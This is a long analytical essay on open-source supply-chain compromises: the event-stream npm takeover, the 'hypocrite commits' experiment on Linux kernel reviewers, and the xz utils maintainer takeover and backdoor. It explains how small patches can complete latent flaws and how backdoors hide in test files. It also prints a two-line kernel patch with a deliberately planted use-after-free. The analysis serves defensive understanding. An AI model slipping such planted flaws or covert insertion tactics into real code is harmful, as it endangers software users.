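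The code was inactive for nearly all of these users; the people at risk were Copay's customers. BitPay first said that no public version contained the code, then confirmed that versions 5.0.2 to 5.1.0 did. According to Wayne, Copay updated its dependencies on 25 September and the release followed on 1 October. The harmful flatmap-stream did not exist on either date, so a later build must have fetched it. BitPay later pinned its dependencies so that most would change only with major releases of the wallet, and limited the web addresses the wallet could contact.

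It is less clear whether anyone lost money. Tarr told Changelog that the attack had failed completely. He understood that the wallet had not been fully released, but BitPay's own account contradicts that. Arvanitis and colleagues write that the attack succeeded and directly affected several users, but they give no figure for losses. A day after the removal, The Next Web's *PSA* (2018) called the extent of any theft unclear.

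### What an unpaid author owes

Many people blamed Tarr. On 26 November he replied under his account name in *statement on event-stream compromise* (dominictarr, 2018). He explained that he had written the package for fun and to learn, and added, "If it's not fun anymore, you get literally nothing from maintaining a popular package." He said that an author cannot sell or rent out such a package, yet remains responsible for it. He also said that sharing publishing rights was common practice on npm, that he had done it before, and that right9ctrl had looked like someone who wanted to help.

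Tarr thought the people who depend on a package should be responsible for it, because they suffer if it breaks. He proposed that they either pay the maintainers or help maintain the package, and he preferred the second. The blunter claim that maintainers owe their users nothing came from Changelog's hosts, who attributed it to the programmer Brett Cannon.

This is hard to dispute as a claim about labour. Tarr had promised nobody years of free work, and event-stream's licence disclaimed any guarantee. One reader replied beneath Tarr's statement that people sometimes have social duties they never asked for, regardless of the licence. That may be true, but a duty to answer strangers' requests indefinitely would be a heavy burden to place on someone for having once shared some code.

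The better objection is that Tarr handed the package over when he could have stopped work and left it as it was, which would have taken no effort. The handover gave the new maintainer a name that thousands of other packages already depended on, along with the power to send them new code. npm did not alert users to the change of maintainer. A member of Changelog's online community suggested that an author who loses interest should say so and let others publish copies under new names, which would have to build their own reputations. The same member gave the example of CanCan, a Ruby package whose users moved to a successor called CanCanCan after its author left.

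Tarr largely accepted this. He called something like it the obvious solution in hindsight, and agreed that whoever gives a package away is responsible for finding out who receives it. He added that an attacker could also publish the new copy and attract users by being helpful. That is true, but each project would have to choose the copy, whereas Copay received right9ctrl's code without choosing to.

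Much of what Tarr handed over was a package that other software installed automatically, rather than the trust of people who had chosen to rely on him. Copay's developers may never have heard of him. The package's later popularity also suggests that many installations were automatic. In September 2026, ecosyste.ms, a site that tracks open-source packages, still showed about 25 million npm downloads a month.

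A stricter check on right9ctrl might not have helped much. Tarr gave him access before he had contributed anything, but right9ctrl then produced several useful-looking commits within two days, and whoever ran the account that later took over xz utils was far more patient. Wayne objects to relying on maintainers' care, since Copay's safety would then require some 1,700 people never to make a mistake. Tarr's preferred remedy, having users of a package help maintain it, has a similar weakness, because right9ctrl appeared to be a user offering that help.

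## The hypocrite-commits experiment on the Linux kernel

The attacker who took over event-stream could publish releases without review. In August 2020 Qiushi Wu, a doctoral student at the University of Minnesota, and Kangjie Lu, an assistant professor there, tested whether Linux kernel reviewers would notice planted flaws. Posing as volunteers, they emailed patches with these flaws to the kernel's developers. Their paper, *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, describes the test and calls such a patch a hypocrite commit, meaning a small change that fixes something minor but creates a much more serious problem. None of the flawed patches got into the kernel, but reviewers overlooked two of the three planted flaws.

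### How kernel developers review patches

Kernel developers receive changes as emailed patches, text files that list the lines to add and remove. A script suggests where to send each patch, usually to the maintainers of that part of the code and one or more public mailing lists. A maintainer who accepts a patch applies it to their own copy of the code, and accepted patches then move to the main version in batches. Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable releases, told Wu by email that developers do not review these batches again because they trust the sender to have reviewed them already.

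The Linux kernel should be a good case for the many-eyeballs assumption because so many people work on it. Wu and Lu count more than 22,000 contributors, and Kroah-Hartman put the number at about 4,000 a year, a quarter of them new. But far fewer people deal with any one patch. One of the test patches went to eight named developers and the public list, and one person replied, though others may have read it.

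### How a small fix can complete a latent weakness

Wu and Lu observe that a security flaw often needs several conditions at once. Their main example is the use-after-free, in which a program releases a piece of memory and then uses it anyway. By then the memory may hold other data, possibly supplied by an attacker. The flaw requires a release, a use, and that the use come after the release. Code that meets only some of these conditions has no bug yet, so bug-finding tools do not report it. Wu and Lu call such a case an immature vulnerability. An attacker only has to add the missing condition, which may take a single line of code.

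"On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software via Hypocrite Commits" gives an example of a plausible fix that accidentally introduced a flaw into the kernel's network code. The kernel counts how many parts of the system are using a device and releases the device's memory when the count reaches zero. After a failed registration the count stayed too high, so someone added one line to lower it, which is normally the right repair. However, another function also ran after such a failure, and it used and released the same memory again. The flaw stayed in the kernel for five years. To catch it, a reviewer had to know what happened in a function that the patch did not touch.

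Wu and Lu collected 138 known kernel vulnerabilities introduced by patches of fewer than 30 lines that were meant to fix minor problems. These made up 9.8% of the vulnerabilities they could trace. Maintainers had written 37.3% of the harmful patches, compared with 47.8% of a sample of 500 recent small patches. By these figures, a small patch from anyone else was about one and a half times as likely to introduce a vulnerability as one from a maintainer. The comparison is rough because the two samples cover different periods. Still, maintainers wrote more than a third of the harmful patches, so shutting out strangers would not prevent many of the vulnerabilities introduced by accident.

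To estimate how often reviewers notice such flaws, Wu and Lu looked at use-after-free bugs in patches from January 2015 to August 2020. They divided the number that reviewers had stopped by the number stopped plus the number that got through:

| Feature of the code | Share that reviewers caught |
|---|---|
| Several parts of the kernel running at the same time | 19.4% |
| Functions that release memory without this being obvious | 36.3% |
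| Two names for the same memory | 38.4% |
| Error-handling code, which seldom runs | 42.0% |
| Baseline for comparison | 56.6% |

Wu and Lu call these figures upper bounds, because some flaws that got through are still undiscovered. That would follow only if they had found every flaw that reviewers stopped. A reviewer may reject a patch for another reason, and then nobody records the flaw. The true rates could therefore be higher or lower.

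An attacker can also submit more than one patch. If reviewers catch 42% of flaws in error-handling code and each attempt is independent, they will catch all three of an attacker's attempts only 7.4% of the time. In practice a reviewer might grow suspicious after catching the first, but the attacker can send the next from a new, free email account.

Finding places to attack took little effort. Wu and Lu wrote tools that reported 921 places where someone might add a release before a use, and 4,657 where someone might add a use after a release. Within a week, one researcher looked through 100 of each and picked three.

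### The five patches of August 2020

The patches came from two Gmail accounts in the names of George Acosta and James Bond. *Retour sur l'affaire des patchs hypocrites de l'université du Minnesota*, a French retrospective, notes that kernel developers usually post under their real names, but finds nothing else in the emails to arouse suspicion. Wu and Lu published the patches and the replies eight months later in the University of Minnesota's *A Full Disclosure of the Case Study of the "Hypocrite Commits" Paper* (2021).

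| Sent | Apparent purpose | Planted flaw | Answer | Merged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 August | Tidy up after an error in a firmware driver | None | None published | No |
| 9 August | Fix a memory leak in the text console | Use-after-free | Refusal | No |
| 20 August | Add an error message to an encryption driver | None, as it turned out | Acceptance | Yes |
| 20 August | Correct a device count in the RapidIO driver | Use-after-free | Request for other changes | No |
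| 21 August | Correct a device count in a flash-memory driver | Double release | Suggestion to move the new lines | No |

The console patch freed some memory after an error, although other code still needed it. To make the patch convincing, "James Bond" included a leak report from an automated testing tool. Jiri Slaby of SUSE rejected it within hours because he remembered that developers had accepted a nearly identical patch in 2019 and then had to undo it. Kroah-Hartman added that he had a whole talk about that earlier change, and commented "Nice name..." on the signature. Wu and Lu say they did not know about the 2019 patch. They reasonably took its original acceptance as proof that such a flaw can pass review, although Slaby caught it this time.

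The encryption patch added one line that prints a message when the driver fails to reserve memory. Wu and Lu had studied such flaws and picked this spot themselves, but at first they wrongly thought the message would use an object that another part of the kernel might already have released. Herbert Xu, the maintainer, applied the patch on 28 August. "George Acosta" then asked whether the order of two calls mattered, and Xu said he did not think so. After further checking, Wu and Lu decided the patch was harmless and let it go in.

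The RapidIO patch also added a single line, placed just above an existing error message (slightly shortened here):

```
put_device(&chdev->dev);
dev_err(&chdev->dev, "kfifo_alloc failed");
```

The new first line lowers the count and may release the device's memory, but the second line then uses the device to print the message. Dan Carpenter of Oracle replied four and a half hours after the patch went out. He found a different use-after-free in the surrounding code and called the function's error handling "kind of rubbish", but did not mention the planted flaw. He also asked for a shared block at the end of the function to lower the count. That would have put the release after the message and removed the flaw shown here without anyone noticing it.

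The patch to the flash-memory driver lowered a device count in three places. A cleanup function already lowered it, so the count would have dropped twice. Miquel Raynal suggested moving the three new lines to one place, which would probably still have lowered the count twice. The next day "James Bond" wrote that he had rechecked the code and found his patch "meaningless", and Raynal thanked him.

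### Where the accounts disagree

The Technical Advisory Board, which advises the Linux Foundation, listed five hypocrite-commits patches in its report of 5 May 2021, as quoted in a reply by kernel developer Pavel Machek (2021). Wu and Lu say that one of the five, dated 4 August, was a sincere fix that they accidentally sent from a false account. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) counts four test patches, one of them valid. Kees Cook (2021), who had sent out the board's report, thanked the university for this clarification.

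Wu and Lu wrote in the paper that they had submitted three patches that introduced use-after-free bugs. They wrote that as soon as a maintainer approved one, they would reveal the flaw, ask the maintainer not to apply the patch, and supply a correct one, and that maintainers had explicitly confirmed this in all three cases. The published emails contain no such exchange. No maintainer approved a flawed patch, and the encryption patch, one of the paper's three cases, was harmless. The closest thing to a warning was the message to Raynal, which passed the planted flaw off as an honest mistake.

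The encryption patch also exposed a weakness in Wu and Lu's safeguard, which relied on a gap between a maintainer's approval and the merge. Xu first replied that he had already applied the patch. If it had contained a real flaw, they would have had to ask him to remove it.

Wu and Lu also wrote that they had reported their findings to the Linux community. On 27 August Wu emailed Kroah-Hartman under his own name to ask how maintainers dealt with malicious contributors, but did not mention that he and Lu were then testing them. Kroah-Hartman answered that everyone makes mistakes and that he trusts people to stay around and fix theirs. This is a sensible rule for accidental flaws, but someone who has planted a flaw does not want to fix it. Wu also claimed that maintainers tend to reject patches against bugs that do not exist yet. Kroah-Hartman replied that "this is not true" and pointed to years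 of work on protective features, yet Wu and Lu wrote in their paper that the community had said it would not accept such patches.

The paper was due to appear at the IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy, a leading security conference. The program committee compared it with the emails and called the description of the patches ambiguous and "in some cases misleading" (IEEE S&P, 2021).

### What three flawed patches can show about review

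Reviewers merged none of the three flawed patches and identified one of the three flaws. Derek Jones, who writes about software engineering research, objected that three patches are too few for any meaningful statistics. Even if reviewers accepted 63% of such patches, they would reject three in a row about one time in twenty, so the result is consistent with both a very good review process and a poor one. Identifying one flaw in three gives a 95% confidence interval of about 1% to 91% for the rate at which reviewers spot such flaws.

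The experiment also had no control group. A proper test would have included many honest patches of the same size from equally unknown accounts. Maintainers reject many newcomers' patches for clumsy coding, so only a comparison could show whether a planted flaw makes rejection more likely. The two harmless patches cannot serve as a control group, since one was accepted and the other apparently received no answer.

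Wu and Lu stopped after the first round of comments on the two driver patches, whereas a real attacker would have made the changes the reviewers asked for and tried again. It is unknown whether the flaws would have survived a second round. Wu and Lu had also chosen the three places because flaws looked easy to hide there, so the results provide little evidence about ordinary patches.

The test's few examples are enough to show that a competent reviewer can read a patch of one to three lines, find other things wrong with it, and still miss the planted flaw. But the 138 past vulnerabilities had already shown this in a far larger sample, collected without deceiving any maintainers. The program committee concluded that the experiments gave no convincing evidence for the paper's main claims. That conclusion is fair for the live test, though somewhat harsh on the analysis of past patches. Larger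 studies have since measured more directly what reviewers miss.

The many-eyeballs claim is about finding flaws, but reviewers can stop a patch without finding its flaw. Carpenter and Raynal protected users by asking for other changes. Review can therefore keep out more flaws than reviewers notice, but this protection is weak against a patient contributor who writes clean code. In the discussion under Edge (2021), *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers*, the commenter wtarreau explained that to confirm a patch fixes a real problem, reviewers would have to repeat all the analysis the contributor claims to have done, and a project of this size would then make very little progress.

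### April 2021: a ban based on a mistaken suspicion

On 6 April 2021 Aditya Pakki, a doctoral student at the same university, sent the kernel developers five patches. Edge reports that two developers objected to one of them within two days. According to It's FOSS, a news site, Al Viro wrote on 19 April that one of Pakki's patches was a "fix that does not fix anything", and that Pakki either understood nothing or was testing the reviewers. By then the developers knew about the paper. Leon Romanovsky looked at four of Pakki's earlier, accepted patches and said three had added security holes.

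On 20 April Kroah-Hartman told Pakki to stop sending patches he knew to be invalid. Pakki replied that they came from a new analysis tool that was not yet accurate, and that the accusations bordered on slander. Kroah-Hartman did not believe him. He announced a ban on all contributions from the university and prepared to remove its earlier ones. He drew up 190 reversals he considered easy and set aside 68 more patches for manual review.

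This soon proved to be an overreaction. Two days later the Technical Advisory Board said that the vast majority of the university's patches seemed to be in good faith (Corbet 2021, *A statement on the UMN mess*). The university later stated that Pakki's five patches had nothing to do with the experiment and that he had sent them in good faith, though they were superfluous and of poor quality. On 29 April, Kroah-Hartman was still writing that developers had found commits from the university's addresses to be in "bad faith". Machek objected that there had been no deception in 2021 and asked whether the kernel developers now owed the university an apology. In a reply that Machek quotes, Cook conceded that the wording was "sub-optimal".

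Kroah-Hartman's suspicion was understandable, since reviewers can't tell from a useless or harmful patch alone whether its author was careless or malicious, and this group had already lied to reviewers once. People had also wondered whether the missing check that caused Heartbleed was deliberate.

The board's members and many other developers then re-reviewed 435 commits, according to Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal*. In the comments under LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), David Wheeler counted 85 developers whom the board thanked for the re-review. Kroah-Hartman dropped his plan to remove the old patches that the reviewers found valid. The reviewers removed the faulty ones and wrote correct replacements where necessary. Some of the university's good-faith patches had caused problems, including at least one by Lu.

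Wu, Lu and Pakki apologized on 24 April, but Kroah-Hartman rejected the apology. He pointed to a letter in which the Linux Foundation and its board had told the university what it had to do first (Slashdot, *University of Minnesota Researchers Send Apology to Linux Kernel Mailing List*). Wu and Lu withdrew the paper on 26 April, writing that they did not want to benefit from an improperly conducted study or have others copy its method (Wu and Lu, 2021). The board recommended that the university review its patches internally before sending them, and on 9 May Cook accepted a further apology.

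### Testing reviewers without their consent

The ethical dispute had begun months earlier, in November 2020, when Lu posted the paper's abstract on Twitter. Four security specialists, including Linderud and Torres-Arias, protested to the conference's chairs in a letter titled *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*. They complained that the paper gave no sign of an ethics review and that the experiment could damage trust between researchers and open-source developers. The chairs told Wu and Lu to consult their university's ethics board, which decided that the work was not research on human subjects. The conference kept the paper, which its reviewers had rated among the top 5% of submissions.

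In *Clarifications on the "hypocrite commit" work (FAQ)*, Wu and Lu (2020) argued that they were studying a process and not individuals, had collected no personal data, and had kept every patch under five lines to save the maintainers' time. They admitted wasting some of that time and apologized. The University of Minnesota's *An open letter to the Linux community* (2021) says they did not ask permission because maintainers who knew of the study would have been on the lookout for the patches.

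This last argument is the only strong one. The process Wu and Lu studied consists of people reading emails, and they measured whether those people noticed something. The ethics board's decision does not help them much either, because it came after the experiment. The program committee later found that the board had received too little detail about the experiment, and called its own request for a retrospective decision a mistake.

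The maintainers objected that someone had used their time and good faith without asking. A commenter on LWN called the outrage manufactured and compared the test to the fake phishing emails that companies send to their own staff. The direct harm was small. Five developers wrote a few short replies, and no planted flaw reached a user. But an employer authorizes a phishing test, and staff have usually agreed to monitoring as part of their jobs. René Mayrhofer, one of the four who signed the letter, added that research ethics allows deception in rare cases where consent would defeat an important purpose, but only under close independent oversight, which Wu and Lu did not have.

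The greater harm came from lost trust. Without the experiment, developers would probably have dismissed Pakki's patches as poor work, and 85 of them would not have spent weeks rereading old commits. The experiment may also have hurt honest newcomers. Edge quotes the kernel developer Guenter Roeck, who told Lu that he was now much less inclined to accept minor fixes from people he did not know.

The program committee disagreed about whether the experiment was strictly human-subjects research. They agreed that it broke US guidelines for ethical computer research, and they set up an ethics review for future papers. The Technical Advisory Board recommended a document on good practice for researchers, and the kernel's documentation now includes such guidelines. They let researchers study public code and mailing lists, but require developers' explicit agreement before anyone experiments on those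 developers.

The committee suggested a controlled experiment on a simulated project, which it believed would have had equal or greater scientific value. Such a test could be run with the reviewers' consent and include hundreds of patches and a proper control group. But reviewers who know they are being studied will probably read more carefully than a tired maintainer with a full inbox, so the test would tend to overstate how much real review catches.

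Wu and Lu proposed in their withdrawal letter that community leaders should approve such work in advance. That would keep the reviewers unaware, but a few leaders probably cannot consent for thousands of developers who do not work for them. It would be better for individual maintainers to volunteer for unannounced tests over, say, a year. They would know that some patches might be fake, but not which ones, and a trusted colleague with a list of the flawed patches could block them before a merge. Knowing this would make the volunteers somewhat more alert than usual, at least at first, so if they still missed many of the flaws, that would be stronger evidence than Wu and Lu's live test produced.

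## xz utils: how an unknown contributor became a maintainer

The false accounts in the kernel experiment sent five patches in less than three weeks. A contributor using the name Jia Tan worked on another open-source project, xz utils, for more than two years and became its second maintainer before adding a backdoor in early 2024.

Xz utils compresses files and includes a library, liblzma, that lets other programs do the same. Lasse Collin designed its .xz format, with some help, between 2005 and 2008. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (Cox, 2024) reports that the format makes files about 30% smaller than the older gzip format, and that people came to use it for Linux kernel images and much else. Collin ran the project, which he described as "an unpaid hobby project", alone and also maintained a separate Java version. *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) found that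 development had nearly stalled before Jia Tan arrived and that only about ten people were active in the project's chat channel.

### Harmless patches and impatient strangers

Jia Tan's first patch, which added a small settings file for text editors, reached the project's mailing list on 29 October 2021. A second patch, a month later, fixed an apparent problem with reproducible builds. Collin merged the first commit under Jia Tan's email address on 7 February 2022, and by late April he had accepted four patches. Jia Tan was also reviewing other people's code, and Przymus and Durieux judge those reviews reasonable even where the code was complicated. Collin could see that the newcomer was capable and kept contributing. Cox considers these early patches harmless even in retrospect.

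On 19 April 2022 Jia Tan sent another patch. Within days, someone named Jigar Kumar complained that nobody had merged it. Kumar wrote, "Patches spend years on this mailing list," when the patch was at most nine days old. Cox dates the first complaint to 22 April, but the emails reproduced in Securelist's *Assessing the Y, and How, of the XZ Utils incident* begin on 27 April.

The complaints continued for two months:

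| Date in 2022 | Message |
|---|---|
| 19 May | Dennis Ens asks whether the Java version is still maintained. Collin apologizes, writes that "my resources are too limited" and says Jia Tan may get a bigger role |
| 7 June | Kumar writes that nothing will progress without a new maintainer and that Collin has lost interest |
| 8 June | Collin denies this, and explains that "longterm mental health issues" and other things have limited what he can do |
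| 14 June | Kumar accuses Collin of choking the project and asks why he is waiting to change maintainer |
| 21 June | Ens expresses sympathy about Collin's health, then suggests that he hand over one of the two versions |
| 22 June | Kumar asks why Jia Tan cannot commit the patch directly |
| 29 June | Collin calls Jia Tan "practically a co-maintainer already" |

This exchange looked less like a campaign to install Jia Tan at the time than it does now. At first, Kumar and Ens asked only for a new maintainer. Collin was the first to mention Jia Tan for a bigger role, and Kumar took up the name a month later. The complaints were also partly true, since one person with little time was maintaining two programs. Ens even asked about a real contributor's improvements, which were still waiting. A reasonable maintainer could have noticed that two strangers with no record in the project were unusually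 insistent, but users of free software are often rude and impatient.

Cox writes that the pressure worked. It probably helped, though Collin had already raised the idea of a bigger role for Jia Tan on 19 May, before the harshest messages. He had also long been thinking about finding a co-maintainer, who he thought would need skill, time and a lasting interest in the project, and Jia Tan seemed to have all three. It is impossible to tell from public records how much the pressure hurried Collin, because he and Jia Tan did much of their work together off the mailing list.

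### What Collin handed over

Jia Tan was merging changes directly by 30 December 2022, fourteen months after the first patch. Dominic Tarr, by contrast, had given away event-stream before the new maintainer contributed anything. Collin shared control of xz utils in several small steps, and each had an ordinary justification:

| Date | Step | What Collin could see then | What only hindsight shows |
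|---|---|---|---|
| 30 November 2022 | Collin replaces his own address for bug reports with one that reaches both maintainers | A colleague sharing the email | The attacker would be among the first to hear of a problem |
| 30 December 2022 | Jia Tan merges a batch of changes directly | A year of sound patches | The attacker no longer needed approval |
| 18 March 2023 | Jia Tan prepares version 5.4.2 | Help with a tedious job | The attacker was moving towards control of the release archives |
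| 20 March 2023 | Jia Tan becomes the contact for OSS-Fuzz, Google's free fuzz-testing service | Routine upkeep | The attacker would receive the bugs it found |
| 19 January 2024 | The project's website moves to GitHub | A site that is easier to edit | The attacker could change what users read there |

Accounts of Jia Tan's first release differ. Cox writes that Jia Tan both built version 5.4.2 and tagged it, which means marking the exact code that belongs to the release. Przymus and Durieux date Jia Tan's first release to December 2022. The best evidence is Collin's later review of Jia Tan's work, published on the website of Tukaani, the group of projects that includes xz utils. Jia Tan signed the tag for 5.4.2, but Collin built and signed the archive himself. Jia Tan's own archives began with versions 5.2.12 and 5.4.3. Who built each archive matters because the builder controls what goes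 into it. Collin has since checked Jia Tan's archives up to version 5.4.6 and found nothing malicious.

Sources also disagree about Jia Tan's role in the project's GitHub organization. Cox writes that Jia Tan joined it in October 2022, whereas Przymus and Durieux write that Jia Tan created it that December and so owned it. Either way, the takeover was never complete. Collin, writing as Larhzu (2024), states that only he ever had access to the main website and the original code server, and that Jia Tan controlled only what was on GitHub. This allowed Collin to move the project back to its old addresses after the attack.

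In June 2023 a contributor named Hans Jansen sent two patches that let the library pick the fastest version of a function when a program starts. Collin reworked them and Jia Tan merged the result. The backdoor later depended on this feature. In July, Jia Tan switched the feature off in the fuzz tests, saying it conflicted with a tool for finding memory errors. Collin had no reason in 2023 to connect the two changes. Cox accepts that both could have been innocent, and Przymus and Durieux leave open whether Jansen's patches were part of the attack.

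Collin's review notes mention small additions to the library that he considered useless but accepted because Jia Tan kept insisting. The archives for version 5.4.5 had the wrong file permissions and ownership data. Collin suspected that Jia Tan had run the wrong command, but Jia Tan would not admit it, even though doing so would have ended Collin's questions. Collin compared the archive with one he had built himself, found no other differences, and let the release go ahead.

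At the time, the co-maintainer's evasiveness about how the archive was made looked like embarrassment over a trivial error, though it looks alarming in hindsight. Collin had also made the comparison that would have exposed extra code. The day after the backdoor became public, Allbery (2024) wrote that the critical moments in such a deception "always look obvious in retrospect", and that nobody can be suspicious enough to catch every sign and still live among other people.

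### Eight malicious commits

Przymus and Durieux investigated whether Jia Tan's behavior revealed the attack. They collected 1,020 commits, 2,944 GitHub events and 307 mailing-list messages, labelled Jia Tan's interactions by hand, and used a program to sort more than 91,000 changed lines into code, documentation, tests and translations. Only eight commits, all from 2024, contained malicious code. Jia Tan's other activity was mostly normal open-source work, such as answering questions, announcing releases, fixing compiler warnings and correcting typos.

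The programmer Alejandro Colomar separately counted 690 commits under Jia Tan's name, so roughly 1% were malicious. The percentage is inexact because his count covers every branch of the code, and the same change can appear on several branches.

Jia Tan contributed more lines of documentation and translations than of code. Przymus and Durieux see this as an easy way to build credibility without attracting close review. They also suspect that Jia Tan replaced the volunteers' translations with machine-made ones. In his review, Collin compared the translation files with the volunteers' versions and found clear reasons for the differences, such as corrected spacing, which casts doubt on that suspicion. Counting lines also inflates the share of translations, since committing one new file from a translator can change hundreds of lines. Jia Tan did demanding programming too, including rewriting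 part of the decompression code at Collin's request. Collin still considers that rewrite good.

The project visibly improved during these years. In the phase when Jia Tan's first commits went in, 65 commits thanked a contributor, more than in any earlier year. Experienced developers began to take part after the move to GitHub. Collin therefore saw good results from trusting Jia Tan, which would have made a maintainer who judged people by their work more confident over time.

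Przymus and Durieux conclude that a malicious contributor is very hard to tell apart from an enthusiastic, skilled volunteer. They point to rapid growth in expertise and an unusual amount of time spent on the project as possible warning signs, but the best newcomers also show these signs. They acknowledge that their study covers only one attack and that they could not read private messages or the full chat history.

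*Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (Welsh, Finnsson and colleagues, 2025) is more optimistic. It proposes software that would watch for several changes in a contributor's behavior at once and direct closer checks to the code involved. In the xz utils data, Jia Tan's file changes averaged 132 lines, compared with 47 for Collin's. Jia Tan's influence on the code base peaked around the time of the malicious commits, some of which came at unusual hours. The writing in Jia Tan's GitHub issues fell into two groups, which might mean that two people shared the account.

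These signs are weaker than they look. A few very large changes can account for the difference in averages, and Collin is the only person in the comparison group. The method used to sort the writing splits any set of texts into as many groups as its user requests, so finding two groups is poor evidence of two writers. Welsh and colleagues note that Jia Tan sometimes submitted harmless code at odd hours too. Most importantly, they looked for anomalies in an account they already knew to be hostile, and did not test how many honest contributors would show the same anomalies.

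Whether such a detector is useful depends on that number. Suppose, for illustration, that one new maintainer in 10,000 is an attacker, and that a detector flags 90% of attackers but only 1% of honest people. Among 10,000 new maintainers, it would flag about 100 honest ones and, on average, 0.9 attackers. More than 99% of the people it flagged would be honest. That would make it a very poor basis for rejecting volunteers, but it could still be worth using to decide which code to review a second time, which is close to what Welsh and colleagues propose.

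### Who was behind the accounts

Kumar and Ens were probably sock puppets. Cox reports that the journalist Brian Krebs found many of the email addresses involved nowhere else online, even in leaked databases. An address used for years usually turns up in at least one leak, so finding no trace of one suggests that someone created it for this purpose. Securelist, a site run by the security company Kaspersky, adds that the addresses similarly combined a name and a number at a free provider, and that the writers made similar mistakes in English. In March 2024, more accounts with such addresses, including Jansen's, urged the Debian distribution to adopt the backdoored version.

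None of this proves the accounts were fake. Plenty of real people have addresses like that, and some open a new one just for mailing lists. Przymus and Durieux found no direct links between the accounts. Cox writes that the addresses did not appear on the project's list again, but Ens wrote to Collin in March 2024 with ordinary questions about why the Java version was slower. Those questions could have come from a real user or from someone maintaining a false identity.

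There is even less evidence about who Jia Tan was. In April 2024, Colomar's *Analysis on who is Jia Tan, and who he could work for* examined the time zones that Jia Tan's computer had attached to 690 commits. Of these, 676 carried the time zone of China and several of its neighbors. The other 14 were two or three hours ahead of Greenwich, depending on the season. Colomar took these 14 as signs of visits to an intelligence agency and suspected Israel.

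joeyh (2024) replied to Colomar that Collin had applied many of the odd commits, so they would carry his time zone, and Nossum (2024) attributed them to "normal boring maintainer edits". Finland, Collin's home country, uses the same time zone that Colomar had attributed to Israel. Two days after proposing his theory, Colomar found the mistake in his own analysis and called it "a red herring". Collin's notes confirm that he and Jia Tan sometimes recorded commits in each other's names by agreement. The remaining commits consistently show the Asian time zone, but they do not reveal where Jia Tan lived, because anyone can set a computer's clock to any zone.

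Fortune (2024) called the operation probably state-sponsored, and many people agree because the attacker was so patient. That patience is weak evidence, since a criminal group or one determined person could also manage a few hours a week of competent programming for two years. Securelist considers both a small team and an individual with several identities possible. It also suggests that Jia Tan may have earned the role honestly and then been manipulated by a team in early 2024. In that case, Kumar and Ens may have been real users whose complaints were a coincidence. This seems the least likely of the three explanations because it requires several suspicious accounts to be innocent, but the public evidence does not rule it out. Collin promised an article on how the attack happened but had not published it by August 2026.

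### The alert of April 2024

On 15 April 2024 the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF) and the OpenJS Foundation, which supports widely used JavaScript projects, warned that others might be trying to take over open-source projects in the same way. In *Open Source Security (OpenSSF) and OpenJS Foundations Issue Alert for Social Engineering*, their heads, Bender Ginn and Arasaratnam, described a series of similar emails that OpenJS had received under different names. The senders asked OpenJS to update a popular project to fix unspecified critical vulnerabilities, and to make them maintainers although they had contributed little to it. OpenJS gave none of them access. Its staff saw a similar pattern at two JavaScript projects outside the foundation and informed the US government's cybersecurity agency.

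The alert leaves out the names of the projects and the text of the emails, so outsiders cannot judge whether these were coordinated attacks or just the work of pushy people who wanted a title. The attempts were cruder than the approach to Collin, because the people who emailed OpenJS had contributed almost nothing, while Jia Tan had done eight months of useful work by the time Collin wrote of a co-maintainer.

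In their alert, Bender Ginn and Arasaratnam list warning signs that include endorsements from unknown accounts, false urgency and requests for maintainer status from newcomers. The first two fit the messages of 2022 fairly well, but no public message shows Jia Tan asking to become a maintainer. They also advise maintainers to be wary of exchanges that leave them feeling inadequate, which is good advice given Collin's apologies. But they acknowledge that their technical recommendations would not stop a persistent attacker. One of these is to have a second developer review every change, even a maintainer's. At xz utils that second developer would have been Collin, who had taken on Jia Tan because he lacked the time to do everything himself. OpenJS also had a council and security policies to rely on when it received the emails, while Collin had to answer Kumar and Ens alone.

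## xz utils: how the backdoor was hidden and how it was found

By early 2024 Jia Tan could change the code of xz utils and publish its release archives without anyone's approval. On 24 February Jia Tan released version 5.6.0, whose archive contained a backdoor. It targeted OpenSSH, a separate program that administrators use to log in to remote computers and run commands on them. The backdoor let its author get past sshd, the part of OpenSSH that runs on the remote computer and decides who may log in. Andres Freund, a database programmer, exposed the backdoor on 29 March, 34 days after the release, in an email to a public security list, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024).

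### How a compression library got into sshd

OpenSSH's own code does not use liblzma, the compression library in xz utils, but some Linux distributions added a dependency on it. Many distributions use systemd to start and supervise services such as sshd, the OpenSSH server. Debian and several others modified sshd to notify systemd when it had finished starting. The change used systemd's library, libsystemd, which also handled compressed logs and needed liblzma for that. When a program starts, Linux loads the libraries it needs and then the libraries those need, and all of this code runs with the program's privileges. On these systems sshd therefore loaded liblzma every time it started.

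Cox notes in his timeline of the attack that Arch Linux, Gentoo and NixOS do not alter sshd in this way, so their copies never loaded liblzma. The other distributions could also have avoided loading it. Lennart Poettering of the systemd project pointed out that the message is a single short text that a program can easily send without the library. Solar Designer (2024), a security developer, quoted him in the discussion after Freund's email.

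Przymus and Durieux think the attacker probably chose xz utils because it offered this way into sshd and had only one maintainer. Even careful reviewers of OpenSSH could not have found the backdoor, because none of it was in OpenSSH's code.

### Where reviewers did not look

A compression library needs test files, including damaged ones, to check that it handles bad input properly. These files are raw data that people can't read as text. Long before Jia Tan arrived, a note in the project's test folder said that many of the files had been made by hand, so no better "source code" existed than the files themselves. On 23 February Jia Tan added new test files, two of which contained the backdoor in scrambled form. One looked like a damaged archive but was a valid one with certain bytes swapped. The other held the code in pieces, with filler between them, and disguised it with a simple cipher.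 *The xz attack shell script* (2024), a companion piece to Cox's timeline, decodes both files step by step.

A reviewer who opened these files would have seen what looked like noise, as expected. But none of the project's tests used the files, a clue that required no decoding. LWN writes that the first file entered the public history well before the release, but by Cox's dates, anyone reading that history had one day to notice.

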